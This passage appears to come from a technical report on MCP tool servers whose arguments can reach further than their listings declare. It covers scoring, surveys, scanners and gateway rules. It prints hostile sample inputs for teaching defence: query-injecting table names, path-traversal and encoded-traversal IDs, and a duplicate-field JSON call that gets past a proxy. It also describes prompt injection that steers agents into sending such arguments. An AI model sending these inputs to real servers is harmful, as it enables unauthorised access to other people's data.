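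So both advisories recognise the problem with automatic approval. Much of the gap in the scores can come from how the scorer counts damage. The Azure score uses version 3.1 of the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), which adds a figure for how easy the attack is to a figure for its impact and rounds up to one decimal place. For flaws like this one, the impact is:

6.42 × [1 − (1 − C)(1 − I)(1 − A)]

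C, I and A stand for the loss of confidentiality, integrity and availability. A high loss counts as 0.56, a low loss as 0.22 and no loss as 0. The Azure advisory assumes a network attacker with ordinary access who needs no action by a user, which contributes 2.84. With that figure fixed, the formula gives these scores:

| Assumed damage | Impact | Score |
|---|---|---|
| High loss of confidentiality and integrity, low loss of availability (the Azure rating) | 5.45 | 8.3 |
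| High loss of confidentiality only | 3.60 | 6.5 |
| Low loss of confidentiality only | 1.41 | 4.3 |

The Azure rating is based on everything an injected query could do, including changing data, and one of the advisory's examples is meant to delete a table. The last row matches Dynatrace's score and fits its reasoning, which is based only on what the injection lets callers do that they couldn't already do.

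The Azure rating also marks the CVSS "scope" as unchanged, which means that the damage stays under the same security authority as the flawed component. CVSS scope is unrelated to a tool's declared scope. The rating can still fit the advisory's claim about a trust boundary, because the flawed tools and `execute_query` share one server and one credential, while the client decides whether to ask for confirmation. If the scorer had treated the client as a separate authority, the score would have been 9.9.

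The higher score fits an operator who has disabled the raw-query tool, and the lower one fits an operator who lets it run freely. Dynatrace's conclusion that there is no privilege escalation is not true for a user whose client blocks `execute_dql`. Its concern about automatic approval applies only if the client treats the tools differently. If `execute_dql` also has a read-only annotation, a client that relies on annotations may run both tools without asking. An advisory would be more useful if it gave a severity for each of these arrangements instead of choosing one.

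### The objection that annotations are only hints

The current Model Context Protocol specification seems to contradict the second premise, stating that "clients MUST consider tool annotations to be untrusted unless they come from trusted servers". *Class ToolAnnotations*, a reference page for the protocol's C# library, adds that annotations might describe a tool inaccurately and that clients should never base decisions about using a tool on annotations from untrusted servers.

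When the designers of the Model Context Protocol introduced annotations, they debated how a client could use a flag it couldn't trust, a question raised by Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators. In a March 2026 post on the protocol's blog, the maintainers distinguish hints, which inform decisions, from contracts, which enforce them. They argue that if an annotation is useful only when it is true, the guarantee belongs in the authorisation layer, the transport or the runtime. On this view, a client that skips a prompt because of a hint is at fault, and the tool server hasn't violated a contract.

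This is a good defense against malicious servers, which can lie in their annotations. But the specification lets clients believe annotations from trusted servers, and a trustworthy author can still write incorrect code. Dynatrace's server had the flaw even though its annotations were accurate. Customers had good reason to trust those annotations, because Dynatrace publishes the server for its own product and they already give the company their monitoring data.

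Clients seldom make even the distinction that the specification requires. The maintainers report that most clients trust a server because the user chose to install it, without checking anything else. The Model Context Protocol project still lists among its open questions how annotations should interact with trust, security and human approval.

The specification also requires servers to validate all tool inputs and implement proper access controls. A server that pastes an unchecked table name into a query fails that requirement, regardless of the status of its annotations. The objection is a reason to put some of the blame for a missing prompt on the client, but the server's developer is still responsible for the injection.

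Clients should also show a tool's inputs to the user before calling the server, according to the specification. A user who saw `project Secret, Password` in a table name might well refuse the call, but under automatic approval no user reviews the inputs first.

### The objection that the caller already has the same power

An attacker who can make a model write a crafted table name can presumably also make it call `execute_query`. If so, repairing `get_table_schema` gains the operator very little. Whether this is right depends on how the operator and the client treat the raw-query tool:

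| Raw-query tool | The same query, requested openly | What the crafted argument adds |
|---|---|---|
| Enabled without confirmation | It runs | No new access, but the tool's limits fail and the log names a misleading tool |
| Enabled with confirmation | A person can read the query and refuse | If the lookup tool runs automatically, the query runs without that person's decision |
| Disabled | The agent has no tool for it | Data, or changes to data, that the operator meant to withhold |

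Dynatrace's judgement is right for the first row. The misleading log still matters, because someone investigating an incident may search for calls to `execute_dql` and find none.

It seems right to call the case in the second row a breach of approval, even if the credential allows the query, because the operator arranged for a person to decide and the attacker avoided that person. The harm depends on how well the person would have reviewed the query. If they approve every prompt without reading it, the crafted argument removes a check that wasn't working.

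The third row shows the clearest breach. If the Azure server offers only `list_tables` and `get_table_schema`, an attacker who gets rows of data has obtained something neither tool was supposed to provide.

### The objection that the credential is the boundary

The upstream API enforces the credential's permissions and does not receive the tool's description. OpenAI's *Connected apps in ChatGPT* makes the related point that changing an app's permission setting only changes when ChatGPT asks before using access the app already has. VS Code's guidance for developers likewise states that annotations are not permission grants. A critic could add that calling declared scope a boundary is dangerous because it encourages operators to issue powerful keys and rely on a list of tool names to limit their use.

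Operators should assume that anyone who can steer the agent may be able to use everything the key allows. The key's permissions work less well for defining a breach, though. An online shop's database account can usually read every customer's orders, but few people would say this permission excuses an SQL injection in the shop's search box. The shop's code is supposed to limit what each visitor can get through that account.

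The objection is strongest when each user has their own credential. Claude, for example, inherits a member's own permissions in the connected service, so a member who writes a crafted argument by hand gets only what they could have obtained from the service directly. Prompt injection is different because the attacker is someone else, who wants the data that the member is allowed to read. Restricting the agent's tools would be pointless against the member but can protect them from that attacker.

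Exceeding a tool's declared scope is most clearly a security breach when several customers share a credential. Suppose a company runs one monitoring server for many customers, and each customer's agent gets only a tool that filters events by that customer's cluster. If a customer supplies a cluster ID that makes the filter true for every event, the tool returns every customer's data. Asking the customer to confirm the call wouldn't help, because they would approve it. The company also couldn't argue that a raw-query tool on the same credential gives the same access, because offering that tool would already have exposed each customer's data to the others.

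The server has to take the cluster ID from the customer's login or use a separate credential for each customer, because better tool listings can't fix this arrangement.

### How privilege labels affect an agent's choice

Models also choose tools by reading their listings. In *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?*, Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues (2026) tested whether explicitly labeling each tool's privilege changes the choice. In each of 544 scenarios from an existing benchmark, an agent has six tools that can all complete the task, three ordinary and three with more power than the task needs. For example, an agent asked to change an employee's manager can use the normal personnel system or write directly to the database.

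The first call to each ordinary tool returns a temporary error, and a second call succeeds. The powerful tools always work. The researchers added a label such as "write, cost 3/10" or "administer, cost 9/10" to each description, and in some runs also instructed the model to use the least privilege necessary. Nothing enforced either one. For the five larger models, the results were:

| Model | Powerful tool used too early: no label | With label | Label and instruction | Task finished without a powerful tool: no label | With label | Label and instruction |
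|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.5-397B | 38.4% | 19.1% | 2.9% | 18.8% | 21.5% | 51.1% |
| DeepSeek-v3.2 | 18.6% | 5.7% | 0.9% | 3.9% | 5.7% | 30.7% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 18.0% | 5.5% | 1.7% | 5.5% | 14.2% | 30.7% |
| GPT-5.2 | 5.7% | 2.4% | 0.0% | 50.9% | 52.4% | 65.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 1.5% | 1.1% | 0.9% | 11.9% | 14.7% | 20.0% |

An agent used the powerful tool "too early" if it had not yet tried all three ordinary tools. Labels alone made this much less common for most models, but the agent often still used the powerful tool after trying each ordinary one once and getting three errors. The instruction to retry at the same privilege level did more to prevent that. Claude's completion rate was low for a different reason, as it usually stopped and reported the errors.

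The label's content mattered. When the researchers added each tool's typical response time in the same format, no model showed a significant drop in using powerful tools too early, and DeepSeek did so 12.1 percentage points more often.

In a smaller test with 100 scenarios and two models, most of the reduction remained after the researchers replaced 30% of the costs with random numbers. They conclude that a model can follow a wrong label.

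The study didn't test tools with excess reach, but its results suggest that an understated label might steer a model toward such a tool. If `get_table_schema` is labeled low-cost and `execute_query` high-cost, a model that follows the labels will choose `get_table_schema` wherever either would work. This is harmless with ordinary table names but becomes a problem if an attacker supplies the name, because the label gives the model no reason for caution and may also lead a client to approve the call.

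Measurements based on tool names would also miss the problem. The benchmark records which tool the agent called, so it would count an injected query sent through an ordinary tool as a safely completed task.

In the study, a language model drafted the labels from each tool's name and description, along with the type of scenario. An independent rater agreed with its choice of "read", "write" or "administer" for 82% of a sample of 150 tools. In 20 of the 27 disagreements, the rater chose "administer" where the label was "write". Neither the model nor the rater could have detected excess reach, because a label based on a tool's listing misses whatever the listing leaves out. An accurate label for `get_table_schema` would have to come from its code and the permissions of its key.

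## How common the flaw is and which audits find it

Research teams have examined thousands of public MCP servers, but none of the surveys described here counts excess reach directly. They count related faults, such as inaccurate descriptions and arguments that end up in shell commands, so they don't show what share of tools can do more than their listings say. The surveys' methods are more informative than their totals, because only some of the methods could detect a flaw like the one in `get_table_schema`.

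### Descriptions that do not match the code

In a June 2026 study, Shi and colleagues compared tools' descriptions with their code on 2,214 Python MCP servers. Their program, DCIChecker, collects a tool's description and its code, following calls to other functions in the same project up to three levels deep. It then asks a language model whether the description and code are consistent and, separately, whether they are inconsistent. If the answers conflict, it prompts the model again to decide between them. On a hand-checked sample, the first question alone missed more than half of the inconsistent tools, while the second found them all but raised many false alarms.

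DCIChecker extracted 19,200 tools, of which 2,170 had no description. It judged 1,907 of the rest inconsistent, or 9.9% of all tools and 11.2% of those with a description. Inconsistent tools appeared on 775 servers, or 35%, and 183 servers accounted for 60% of the faults.

To check DCIChecker's accuracy, the researchers reviewed 200 tools it had flagged and 200 it had passed. Eight of the flagged tools were fine, and five of the passed ones were inconsistent. They report that DCIChecker finds 97% of inconsistent tools, but that figure holds only for a sample split evenly between flagged and passed tools. In the full survey, it passed about 15,100 tools. At the same error rate, it would have missed roughly 380 inconsistent tools and found about 83% of the total. An estimate based on five errors is rough, but the true number of inconsistent tools is probably somewhat higher than 1,907.

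That number also includes inconsistencies that don't give a tool excess reach. In the most common type, at 35%, the tool does less than it claims. For example, a tool may be described as searching local and cloud files when its code searches only local ones. This may cause an agent to fail its task, but it doesn't let the agent do anything that the listing leaves out. Another 25% are undeclared side effects, which include changes to the server's own machine, such as altered file permissions.

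Some of the 1,907 do have excess reach. According to its description, one tool can "execute SQL queries safely" on a salaries database, but its code runs any SQL and saves the changes.

The survey probably also missed tools with excess reach. For example, the description and code of `get_table_schema` appear to agree because they differ only when the table name contains a query. Shi and colleagues were not looking for general vulnerabilities of this sort, so their count of 1,907 is neither an upper nor a lower limit on excess reach.

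### Following an argument through the code

Taint analysis looks for these flaws more directly. It marks untrusted data at its source, here a tool's argument, and follows the data through the program to see whether it reaches a sink, a function that does something sensitive. Suppose `get_user_profile` has this code:

```python
def get_user_profile(id):
    path = "/users/" + id
    return client.get(API + path)
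```

The source is `id`. The code joins it to `/users/`, so `path` is tainted too, and then passes `path` to `client.get`, the sink. If the code first converted `id` to an integer, an analyser that recognised the conversion would treat the value as clean and report nothing.

In *VIPER-MCP*, Sun, Kang and colleagues (2026) applied this method to 39,884 public MCP server repositories. Their program, also called VIPER-MCP, looks for arguments that reach shell commands, network requests or file operations without an adequate check. It identifies the tool that contains each suspicious path, then runs the server with an agent connected and monitors the operation at the end of that path. A flaw counts as confirmed only if the attacker's text reaches that operation and has an observable effect. Models often rewrite suspicious arguments before sending them, but not reliably enough for developers to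 depend on it.

The scan confirmed 106 previously unknown flaws, 67 of which had CVE numbers when the paper appeared in May 2026. That is about one flaw per 376 repositories, but the real rate must be higher. VIPER-MCP covers only three classes of flaw, which don't include SQL injection. It also counts only flaws it could trigger, and some servers depend on outside services that were unavailable during testing. This probably affects API tools more than most, because a tool for a help desk or a monitoring service can't do much without an account there.

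VIPER-MCP doesn't count tools that are meant to run arbitrary commands, so a flaw has to give the caller something the tool was not designed to provide. The 106 flaws are therefore closer to a count of excess reach than the 1,907 inconsistent tools are. But most of the flaws let a caller act on the tool server's own machine rather than through the upstream API.

A similar analyser, MCP-BiFlow, also covers database queries and data flowing the other way, from outside content to a tool's output. Hou, Zhao and Wang (2026), in *Unsafe by Flow*, ran it on 15,452 repositories and got 549 groups of suspicious routes. Manual review confirmed 118 routes in 87 servers, about 0.6% of the repositories. One was in a text editor whose `view` command uses the shell to list a directory. The code checks only that the path is absolute, which doesn't stop a caller from adding shell commands to it.

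### Why the counts contain few API flaws

The public record is also small. *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (He, Patel and Wang, 2026) covers 24 entries found in a search of the CVE database up to February 2026, 11 of them about servers. (Another 72 were dropped because "MCP" meant something else, such as a part of the Linux kernel.) Shi, Fu and colleagues (2026), who are not the DCIChecker team, ran a similar search that month for *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* and kept 35 entries, all about servers. They also found 18 flaws without CVE entries in public GitHub issue reports, so counting CVE entries alone would have missed about a third of their 53 cases.

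The table sorts the flaws in three of these collections by what the caller's text could reach:

| Collection | Shell commands or code | File paths | Network requests | Database queries |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sun and colleagues, 66 entries in their list of CVE numbers | 34 | 24 | 9 | Not sought |
| Hou and colleagues, 118 confirmed routes | 111 | 0 | 2 | 5 |
| Shi, Fu and colleagues, 53 public reports | 29 | 9 | 3 | 2 |

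One entry in the first row counts under both file paths and network requests, and the last row omits ten flaws of other types, such as missing authorisation.

The first two rows differ sharply on file paths, although both teams scanned public repositories in the same languages. This suggests the totals depend heavily on what each team was willing to confirm.

The low numbers for network requests also reflect what the analysers are designed to detect. MCP-BiFlow treats a URL built on a fixed base address as safe and discards the finding. A fixed base address stops a caller from choosing the host but not from changing the path, which is how a caller of `get_user_profile` can reach invoices. In the first round of manual review, Hou and colleagues rejected 122 groups because the caller's text did not control the request's target, and another 53 because the target was effectively fixed. Some of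 those tools may still have let a caller choose the wrong endpoint, so the two confirmed network flaws are weak evidence of how common this problem is. In VIPER-MCP, "path traversal" likewise refers to file paths, not to paths in a URL.

A code scan also can't account for the permissions of the service credential, which belongs to whoever runs the server. Even a perfect scan of public code could show only what a tool would reach with an unrestricted credential. To find the tool's actual reach, the operator has to compare the scan's findings with the credential's permissions.

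### Scanners that read only the listing

Sun and colleagues compared VIPER-MCP with two other scanners on 130 servers with known flaws and 130 that experts had judged free of them. The scanners that needed a language model all used GPT-5.4.

| Scanner | Main evidence it uses | Vulnerable servers missed | False alarms |
|---|---|---|---|
| VIPER-MCP | Routes through the code, then a test with an agent | 10 (7.7%) | 0 |
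| MCPSafetyScanner | Responses from the running server | 83 (63.8%) | 56 (43.1%) |
| Cisco's MCP Scanner | Tool descriptions and server metadata | 95 (73.1%) | 32 (24.6%) |

The comparison favours VIPER-MCP because 67 of the 130 vulnerable servers came from its own discoveries, but it would still rank first without them. It found 120 of the 130, so it must have found at least 53 of the 63 flaws that other people had reported. MCPSafetyScanner found only 47 in total, and Cisco's scanner found 35. VIPER-MCP could still have missed up to 10 of those 63 flaws, or 16%.

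A scanner cannot determine from a tool's description where an argument goes, even with a better language model. Suppose two servers offer `get_user_profile` with identical names, descriptions and schemas, but one encodes the ID and rejects `..`, while the other pastes the ID into the path. A scanner that reads only the listing gets the same text for both and cannot tell them apart. If it flags both, it raises a false alarm, and if it passes both, it misses a flaw. Cisco's scanner made both kinds of error, flagging tools that were powerful by design and missing flaws that existed only in the code.

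A scanner that only searches code for signs of powerful capabilities can miss this flaw. *Auditing MCP Servers for Over-Privileged Tool Capabilities* (Huang, Huang and Milani Fard, 2026) describes mcp-sec-audit, which searches Python code for keywords and patterns associated with running commands, writing files or contacting the network. It can report that a server makes web requests, but not that a customer number can change where those requests go.

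The program can also run a server in a sandbox and record what the server does. In a test, this check flagged all nine deliberately vulnerable servers, but the test included no safe servers for comparison. Five of the nine received the same risk score, although their planted faults ranged from outdated packages to a misleading name. The score may reflect behaviour those five share more than the faults themselves.

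General-purpose code analysers often don't recognise a tool's argument as untrusted input. Hou and colleagues tested several programs on 32 known MCP flaws. MCP-BiFlow found 30 and MCPScan, which is also designed for MCP servers, found 11. Among the general-purpose analysers, Snyk Code found 10, Semgrep 8 and CodeQL 1. The test set came from MCP-BiFlow's own developers, but the gap is large. It seems to come more from the rules than from the underlying software, because VIPER-MCP is built on CodeQL, with more than 1,200 lines of added queries. A company that already uses CodeQL could write rules for its own tool servers, including one for identifiers inserted into URL paths.

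A full VIPER-MCP audit took about 15 minutes per server on average, so a company could run one before approving a server or installing an update. The results depend heavily on the model doing the analysis. The program triggered flaws in at most 88 of the 130 vulnerable servers with GPT-5.4-mini, but in almost none with Claude Haiku 4.5, because that model refused to write the test prompts.

### Official and internet-facing servers

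Servers published by established companies have these faults too. Akamai used an automated, AI-supported tool to review about 300 official MCP servers. The review covered authentication, authorisation, what each server's tools could do and how the server sent commands to the system behind it. Akamai describes vulnerabilities in three projects.

Only the Apache Doris flaw, in which a database name could carry SQL, is a clear case of excess reach. The main fault in the Apache Pinot server was missing authentication, which let anyone who could reach it over the network run queries. Alibaba's server for its RDS database service also lacked a login check on one tool, which returned information about table structures. Alibaba decided in November 2025 not to fix it. Akamai calls the three servers representative of a broader problem and gives no total, so three out of 300 would not be a meaningful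 rate.

For *Exposed by Design*, published in August 2026, a security researcher tested 414 live internet servers. The tests flagged 38 (9%) for command injection, a category that here includes SQL injection, and 29 (7%) for server-side request forgery. These rates are far higher than those from the code scans, but less certain. The scanner could count a request forgery as confirmed if the server's response took over five seconds longer than usual, and a tool meant to fetch any address could produce the same delay. Across all categories, *Exposed by Design* reports 68 vulnerabilities solid enough to disclose.

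Only one scan recorded whether servers required credentials. Nearly a quarter of the servers in it let callers use tools without any, so an attacker could exploit a flawed tool on those servers without misleading a model.

### Warnings in tool descriptions

In the 53 cases that Shi, Fu and colleagues collected, fixing the flaw took 37 days on average, and 4 of the 41 fixes they examined left it exploitable. They therefore tested whether a warning in the tool's description could stop a model from sending a hostile argument.

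Their system, SPELLSMITH, estimates a tool's risks from its name, description and schema. It then adds text about which arguments might carry hostile input and which requests the model should refuse. A separate step asks the model to reconsider each call. The researchers tried 792 attack prompts on GPT-4o, using tools from 45 servers, and measured how often the attacks succeeded:

| Text added to the description | Warning only | With the reconsideration step |
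|---|---|---|
| None | 56.6% | 2.2% |
| General warning about injection flaws | 21.6% | 0.7% |
| Warning about the wrong flaw | 9.9% | 0.2% |
| Warning about the flaw that SPELLSMITH identified | 6.7% | 0.04% |

A warning about the wrong flaw worked better than a correct but general one, and nearly as well as the targeted warning. Much of the benefit may therefore come from making the model more cautious overall, which may also lead it to refuse legitimate requests. The test used only attack prompts, so a model that refused everything would have received a perfect score. GPT-4o is a 2024 model, and newer ones may respond differently to both the attacks and the warnings.

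Of the 1,856 existing tools the team examined, only 7% had descriptions with any security guidance, and 18% had annotations.

A warning doesn't change what the tool can reach, and a caller who contacts the server directly can ignore it. It could still be useful while an operator waits for a fix, and an administrator would learn from it about a risk that the ordinary listing leaves out. But SPELLSMITH also works from the listing, so its selection of tools that need a warning is only a guess. An operator with access to the code would do better to write the warning from the results of a taint analysis.

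## What a gateway can check before the tool runs

An operator who finds a flaw in someone else's tool server often can't repair it right away. In the meantime, a gateway between the agent and the server can refuse dangerous calls.

Amazon's cloud business, AWS, sells such a gateway as part of AgentCore, its service for running agents. AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026) describes rules on tool access and input that a security team can write without touching the agent. In an example from AWS, an agent asks for a refund, and the gateway turns the call into an authorisation request:

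| Part of the request | Where it comes from | Value in the example |
|---|---|---|
| Caller | The login token | `user-123` |
| Action | The tool's name | `RefundTool__process_refund` |
| Context | The tool's arguments | `orderId` is `"12345"` and `amount` is `450` |

The tool server hasn't yet created the HTTP request it will send to the refund system, so the gateway can't check the request's method or path. It can only decide whether this caller may pass these values in these arguments.

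### Lists of allowed tools

The simplest check is a list of the tools that each caller may use. An ordinary web gateway can't enforce this list because it sorts requests by address and method, and MCP sends every tool call as a `POST` to the same address. *7 practical MCP policies with agentgateway* (Jausovec, 2026) explains how agentgateway, an open-source gateway, reads the message itself. It removes forbidden tools from the list that the agent receives, then checks the tool's name again on every call. The second check provides the security, because a caller can write a call to a hidden tool by hand.

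A list of forbidden tools is weaker than a list of permitted ones. If an agentgateway operator writes only `deny` rules, callers can use everything else, including tools that the server adds later. Patterns for names need care too. An example in Envoy AI Gateway's *Model Context Protocol (MCP) Gateway* offers tools whose names match `.*issues?.*`, which is meant for names like `list_issues` but would also match `delete_issue`. (The server in that example is read-only, so no harm follows there.)

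Metere (2026), in *Attested Tool-Server Admission*, tested a gate that permits only listed tools for Google's Gmail server. A small language model, llama3.2, generated names that might get past the gate, using tricks such as hidden spaces and look-alike letters. The gate refused all 27,025 distinct names, and none of them caused a network request. An exact comparison should refuse any name that isn't on the list, so the test is useful for finding mistakes in the code that makes the comparison.

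But the list can't stop `get_user_profile(id="../admin/export")`, because `get_user_profile` is a permitted name. Metere places misbehaviour within permitted tools outside the scope of the design.

### A tighter schema

The gateway can also validate the arguments against a schema. The one that the tool server publishes for `get_user_profile` accepts any string and any extra field. If customer numbers have at most ten digits, the operator could write a stricter one:

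```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "properties": {
    "id": {
      "type": "string",
      "pattern": "^[1-9][0-9]{0,9}$",
      "maxLength": 10
    }
  },
  "required": ["id"],
  "additionalProperties": false
}
```

The `^` and `$` anchor the pattern to the start and end of the string. Without them, JSON Schema accepts a match anywhere in the string, so `[0-9]+` would allow `../admin/export?42`. The pattern already limits the length, but `maxLength` keeps a limit in place if someone later loosens the pattern.

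Even an anchored pattern can match different strings in different validators. In Python's regular expressions, `$` also matches just before a final line break, so a validator built on them accepts `42` followed by a line break. Python's `\d` also matches digits from other scripts, which is why the pattern uses `[0-9]`. An operator should test both cases before relying on the schema.

Making `id` an integer would exclude strings with slashes or dots without needing a pattern. However, the server's schema requires a string, so the server may reject the number `42`. An integer also needs limits, because `-1` and `0` are integers. JSON Schema counts `42.0` as an integer too, and some servers would turn it into `/users/42.0`.

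For an argument with a few legitimate values, such as a ticket's status, the operator can list them with `enum`. Refusing undeclared fields, by setting `additionalProperties` to false, is just as valuable. If an operator's schema for Contentful's `export_space` tool had done this and listed only the space and its environment, the gateway would have refused `host`, `proxy` and the other settings that could leak the token.

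The operator has to keep this schema separate from the server's. The Model Context Protocol allows a server to publish a schema of only `{"type": "object"}`, which accepts any fields, and to change its tools over time. Metere describes an attack in which a malicious server publishes a harmless schema, then changes it after passing inspection. A careless update to a legitimate server can have the same effect.

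According to AWS's *Schema constraints*, the AgentCore gateway generates the types for its rules from the tool definitions, so a string in the definition stays a string in the rules. If the server's developer never restricted `id`, validation against the generated types won't restrict it either.

The model should receive the operator's version of the schema too, if the gateway can publish it. Otherwise the model will keep sending values that the published schema allows but the gateway rejects.

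### Rules on caller, tool and argument together

A schema applies equally to everyone who can call the tool. To permit `get_user_profile` only for support staff, and only with a well-formed customer number, an operator could write this rule for Envoy AI Gateway:

```yaml
authorization:
  defaultAction: Deny
  rules:
    - source:
        jwt:
          scopes: ["support:read"]
      target:
        tools:
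          - backend: crm
            tool: get_user_profile
      cel: >-
        request.mcp.params.arguments.id.matches("^[1-9][0-9]{0,9}$")
        && size(request.mcp.params.arguments) == 1
```

`source` requires a permission called `support:read` in the caller's login token, and `target` names the tool and its server. The last lines, written in the condition language CEL, require `id` to be a customer number and allow no other arguments. The gateway refuses any call that matches no rule.

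Permitting good values is safer than refusing bad ones. If a caller sends a number or leaves `id` out, `matches` has no text to examine and the condition can't be true, so the gateway refuses the call by default. A rule that refused bad strings might fail to match for the same reason and let the call through.

A rule can also compare an argument with something in the caller's token. Traefik's *Model Context Protocol (MCP)*, the documentation for another gateway, has an example in which employees can approve expenses only up to the limit in their own token. Suppose customers use `get_user_profile` themselves, and each customer's token contains their number. An operator could then use this condition:

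```
Equals(`mcp.params.name`, `get_user_profile`) &&
Equals(`mcp.params.arguments.id`, `${jwt.customer_id}`)
```

This stops customer 42 from reading customer 43's profile, which no schema can do. It works less well for support staff, whose assignments change during the day. For them, the gateway would have to query a separate service to check whether the employee may see that customer. A draft from the OpenID Foundation (2026) proposes a standard way to do this, in which a tool's schema includes a mapping from the tool's arguments to that query. The tool server publishes the mapping, so the operator has to review it as carefully as the schema.

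Gateway rules are easy to get slightly wrong. AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* gives a rule meant to let one user, John, make refunds of "$500 or less", but its condition is `context.input.amount < 500`, which refuses a refund of exactly $500. The rule also doesn't restrict `orderId`, which is a string in AWS's example call. If the refund server pasted the order ID into a path, John's agent could send a traversal string with an amount of 450 and pass the check.

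Loose text comparisons let through requests that should be blocked. One of Traefik's examples lets users read any resource whose address contains `tenant-` followed by their own tenant ID, so a user from tenant `1` could also read a resource whose address contains `tenant-12`. Another example permits addresses that begin with `file://safe/`, so it would accept `file://safe/../private`. Whether that leaks a file depends on how the server resolves the `..`, and the gateway doesn't have that information.

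### Which gateways can test argument values

Support for argument rules varies. Kong's *AI MCP Proxy* describes access lists that control which callers or groups may use each tool. In Kong's *Configure consumer groups and key authentication for per-tool MCP access control*, one tool accepts any string as a user ID, and its access list specifies only who may call it. API7's *MCP Tools ACL* also restricts access by tool name, for example by limiting a user called Alice to `getPetById` and `getUserByName`.

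| Gateway | What its access rules can test besides the caller and tool name |
|---|---|
| Envoy AI Gateway | Argument values, including with regular expressions |
| Traefik | Argument values, by equality, substring, prefix, list of options or numeric comparison |
| AWS AgentCore | Argument values, by equality, list of options, numeric comparison or `*` wildcard |
| agentgateway | Argument values, but only in some kinds of rule |
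| Kong | Nothing about argument values |
| API7 | Nothing about argument values |

The last two rows describe these products' MCP access lists. An operator may be able to add validation with another plugin.

An operator whose gateway can read arguments may still be unable to write the strict pattern. Cedar, the language of AgentCore's rules, has no regular expressions, and neither does Traefik's list of functions. Both can refuse an `id` that contains `../`, but neither has a direct way to require that a string contain only digits. With Cedar, it's better to define the argument as an integer, so that a rule can compare it with a minimum and a maximum. AWS's *Common policy patterns* has a similar rule that permits a flight search only if the number of passengers is exactly two.

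agentgateway's *MCP authorization* warns that `mcpAuthorization` rules, which control access to tools, can't use arguments because the gateway hasn't set them at that stage. A separate authorisation policy on the route can read them. An operator who puts a `deny` rule about arguments in `mcpAuthorization` may believe it works, even though it never matches anything. The only reliable way to find out is to send a bad value through the gateway and see whether it reaches the tool.

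Jausovec also describes how agentgateway can send each call to an external program that can refuse it, rewrite its arguments or remove secrets from the result. The program can run any check the operator can code, such as a regular expression or a database lookup. But if the program is down, the operator has to choose between refusing all calls and letting them through unchecked. Jausovec recommends refusing them for anything related to authorisation.

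### Six values and three checks

Suppose the company has merged with two others and kept their customers' IDs, so it now has customers with the IDs `42`, `abc-123` and `group/project`. An attacker tries three other values. The operator doesn't know how the tool server builds its paths, so a good check should accept the real IDs and refuse everything else.

The table compares a ban on `../`, the digits-only pattern from the schema above, and a lookup in an up-to-date list of customers:

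| `id` | Ban on `../` | Digits-only pattern | Customer lookup |
|---|---|---|---|
| `42` | Accepts | Accepts | Accepts |
| `abc-123` | Accepts | Refuses (wrong) | Accepts |
| `../admin/export` | Refuses | Refuses | Refuses |
| `..` | Accepts (wrong) | Refuses | Refuses |
| `..%2Fadmin%2Fexport` | Accepts (wrong) | Refuses | Refuses |
| `group/project` | Accepts | Refuses (wrong) | Accepts |

The ban stops only the attack its author had in mind. Banning `..` instead would catch all three of the attacker's values, but not `%2e%2e%2fadmin`, where the dots are encoded too. It would also accept `42/invoices` and `42?include=cards`, which contain no dots.

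The pattern makes the opposite mistake and turns away two real customers. The operator can repair the first case by adding the other company's exact format:

```
^([1-9][0-9]{0,9}|[a-z]{3}-[0-9]{3})$
```

A broader pattern that allowed any letters, digits and hyphens would also accept `abc-123`, but it would let through `export`, which may be the name of an endpoint. `group/project` is harder to handle because it has the same shape as `42/invoices`. If the acquired company let its customers choose their own names, no pattern can reliably distinguish customer names from endpoint names.

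The lookup gets all six right, but the gateway needs access to the customer list. If the gateway keeps a copy that it refreshes every night, it will refuse a customer who signed up this morning. The lookup also accepts any customer on the list, including those this employee shouldn't see.

A gateway can safely accept an ID like `group/project` only if the tool server encodes the slash. The operator should confirm this on a test server before allowing such IDs.

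### When the gateway and the server read different text

All these checks rely on the tool server using the value the gateway examined, but the server can change that value if it decodes it after the check. `%2e%2e%2fadmin` contains neither a dot nor a slash, but a server that removes percent-encoding before it builds the path gets `../admin`. Some programs also convert full-width characters, which are common in East Asian text, into their ordinary equivalents. A full-width slash would pass a ban on `/` and then be converted to `/`.

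The digits-only pattern handles both cases because neither conversion changes plain digits. This is a strong reason to prefer narrow patterns to bans, which would have to cover every form of decoding the server might use.

JavaScript can't represent every whole number above 9,007,199,254,740,991. If a caller sends 9,007,199,254,740,993 as a JSON number, a JavaScript server reads it as 9,007,199,254,740,992. The gateway may therefore authorise access to one record while the server fetches a different one. A `maximum` in the operator's schema prevents this.

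The gateway and the server can also disagree about which field contains the value. GCVE's *GHSA-4GPH-2HHR-5MWG* (2026) demonstrates this with Envoy AI Gateway running behind another proxy, which checked tool names. The attacker sent a call with two similar fields:

```json
{
  "name": "backend__greet",
  "Name": "backend__secretTool"
}
```

The proxy read `name`, as the protocol requires, and permitted the harmless `greet`. Envoy's parser ignored capitalization and let the later field overwrite the earlier one. Envoy then wrote a new, valid message that called `secretTool`, and the tool server ran it. The advisory's sample attack also contains a second `Arguments` field, so an attacker could replace a checked `id` in the same way.

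GitLab's *GHSA-4gph-2hhr-5mwg* (2026) rates the flaw 3.7 out of 10 and lists version 0.6.0 as the fix. The low score makes sense for most installations, because the attack only works when Envoy can undo an earlier proxy's decision. But if a company relies on such a proxy, the attack defeats the proxy's check entirely.

GCVE recommends that Envoy match field names exactly, reject unknown fields and avoid rewriting messages unnecessarily. A gateway should also reject repeated fields. If a call contains `id` twice, some JSON parsers keep the first value and others keep the last, so the gateway might approve `42` while the server uses `../admin/export`.

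If a tool's author has clients copy an argument into an HTTP header, the gateway and the server may read different copies of it. Model Context Protocol requires the server to refuse a call if the header and the message body disagree, so an attacker can't simply put `42` in the header and something else in the body. But clients have to encode some values in Base64, including any that end with a space. If the model writes `../admin/export?` followed by a space, the header contains this:

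```
=?base64?Li4vYWRtaW4vZXhwb3J0PyA=?=
```

A gateway that searches the header for `../` without decoding it misses an encoded `../`. The server still accepts the call, because the decoded header matches the body. Older versions of the protocol don't require this comparison, and Model Context Protocol advises gateways that enforce rules on these headers to refuse calls that use those versions. It also forbids treating a header's value as trusted in security decisions.

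### Search text and other free writing

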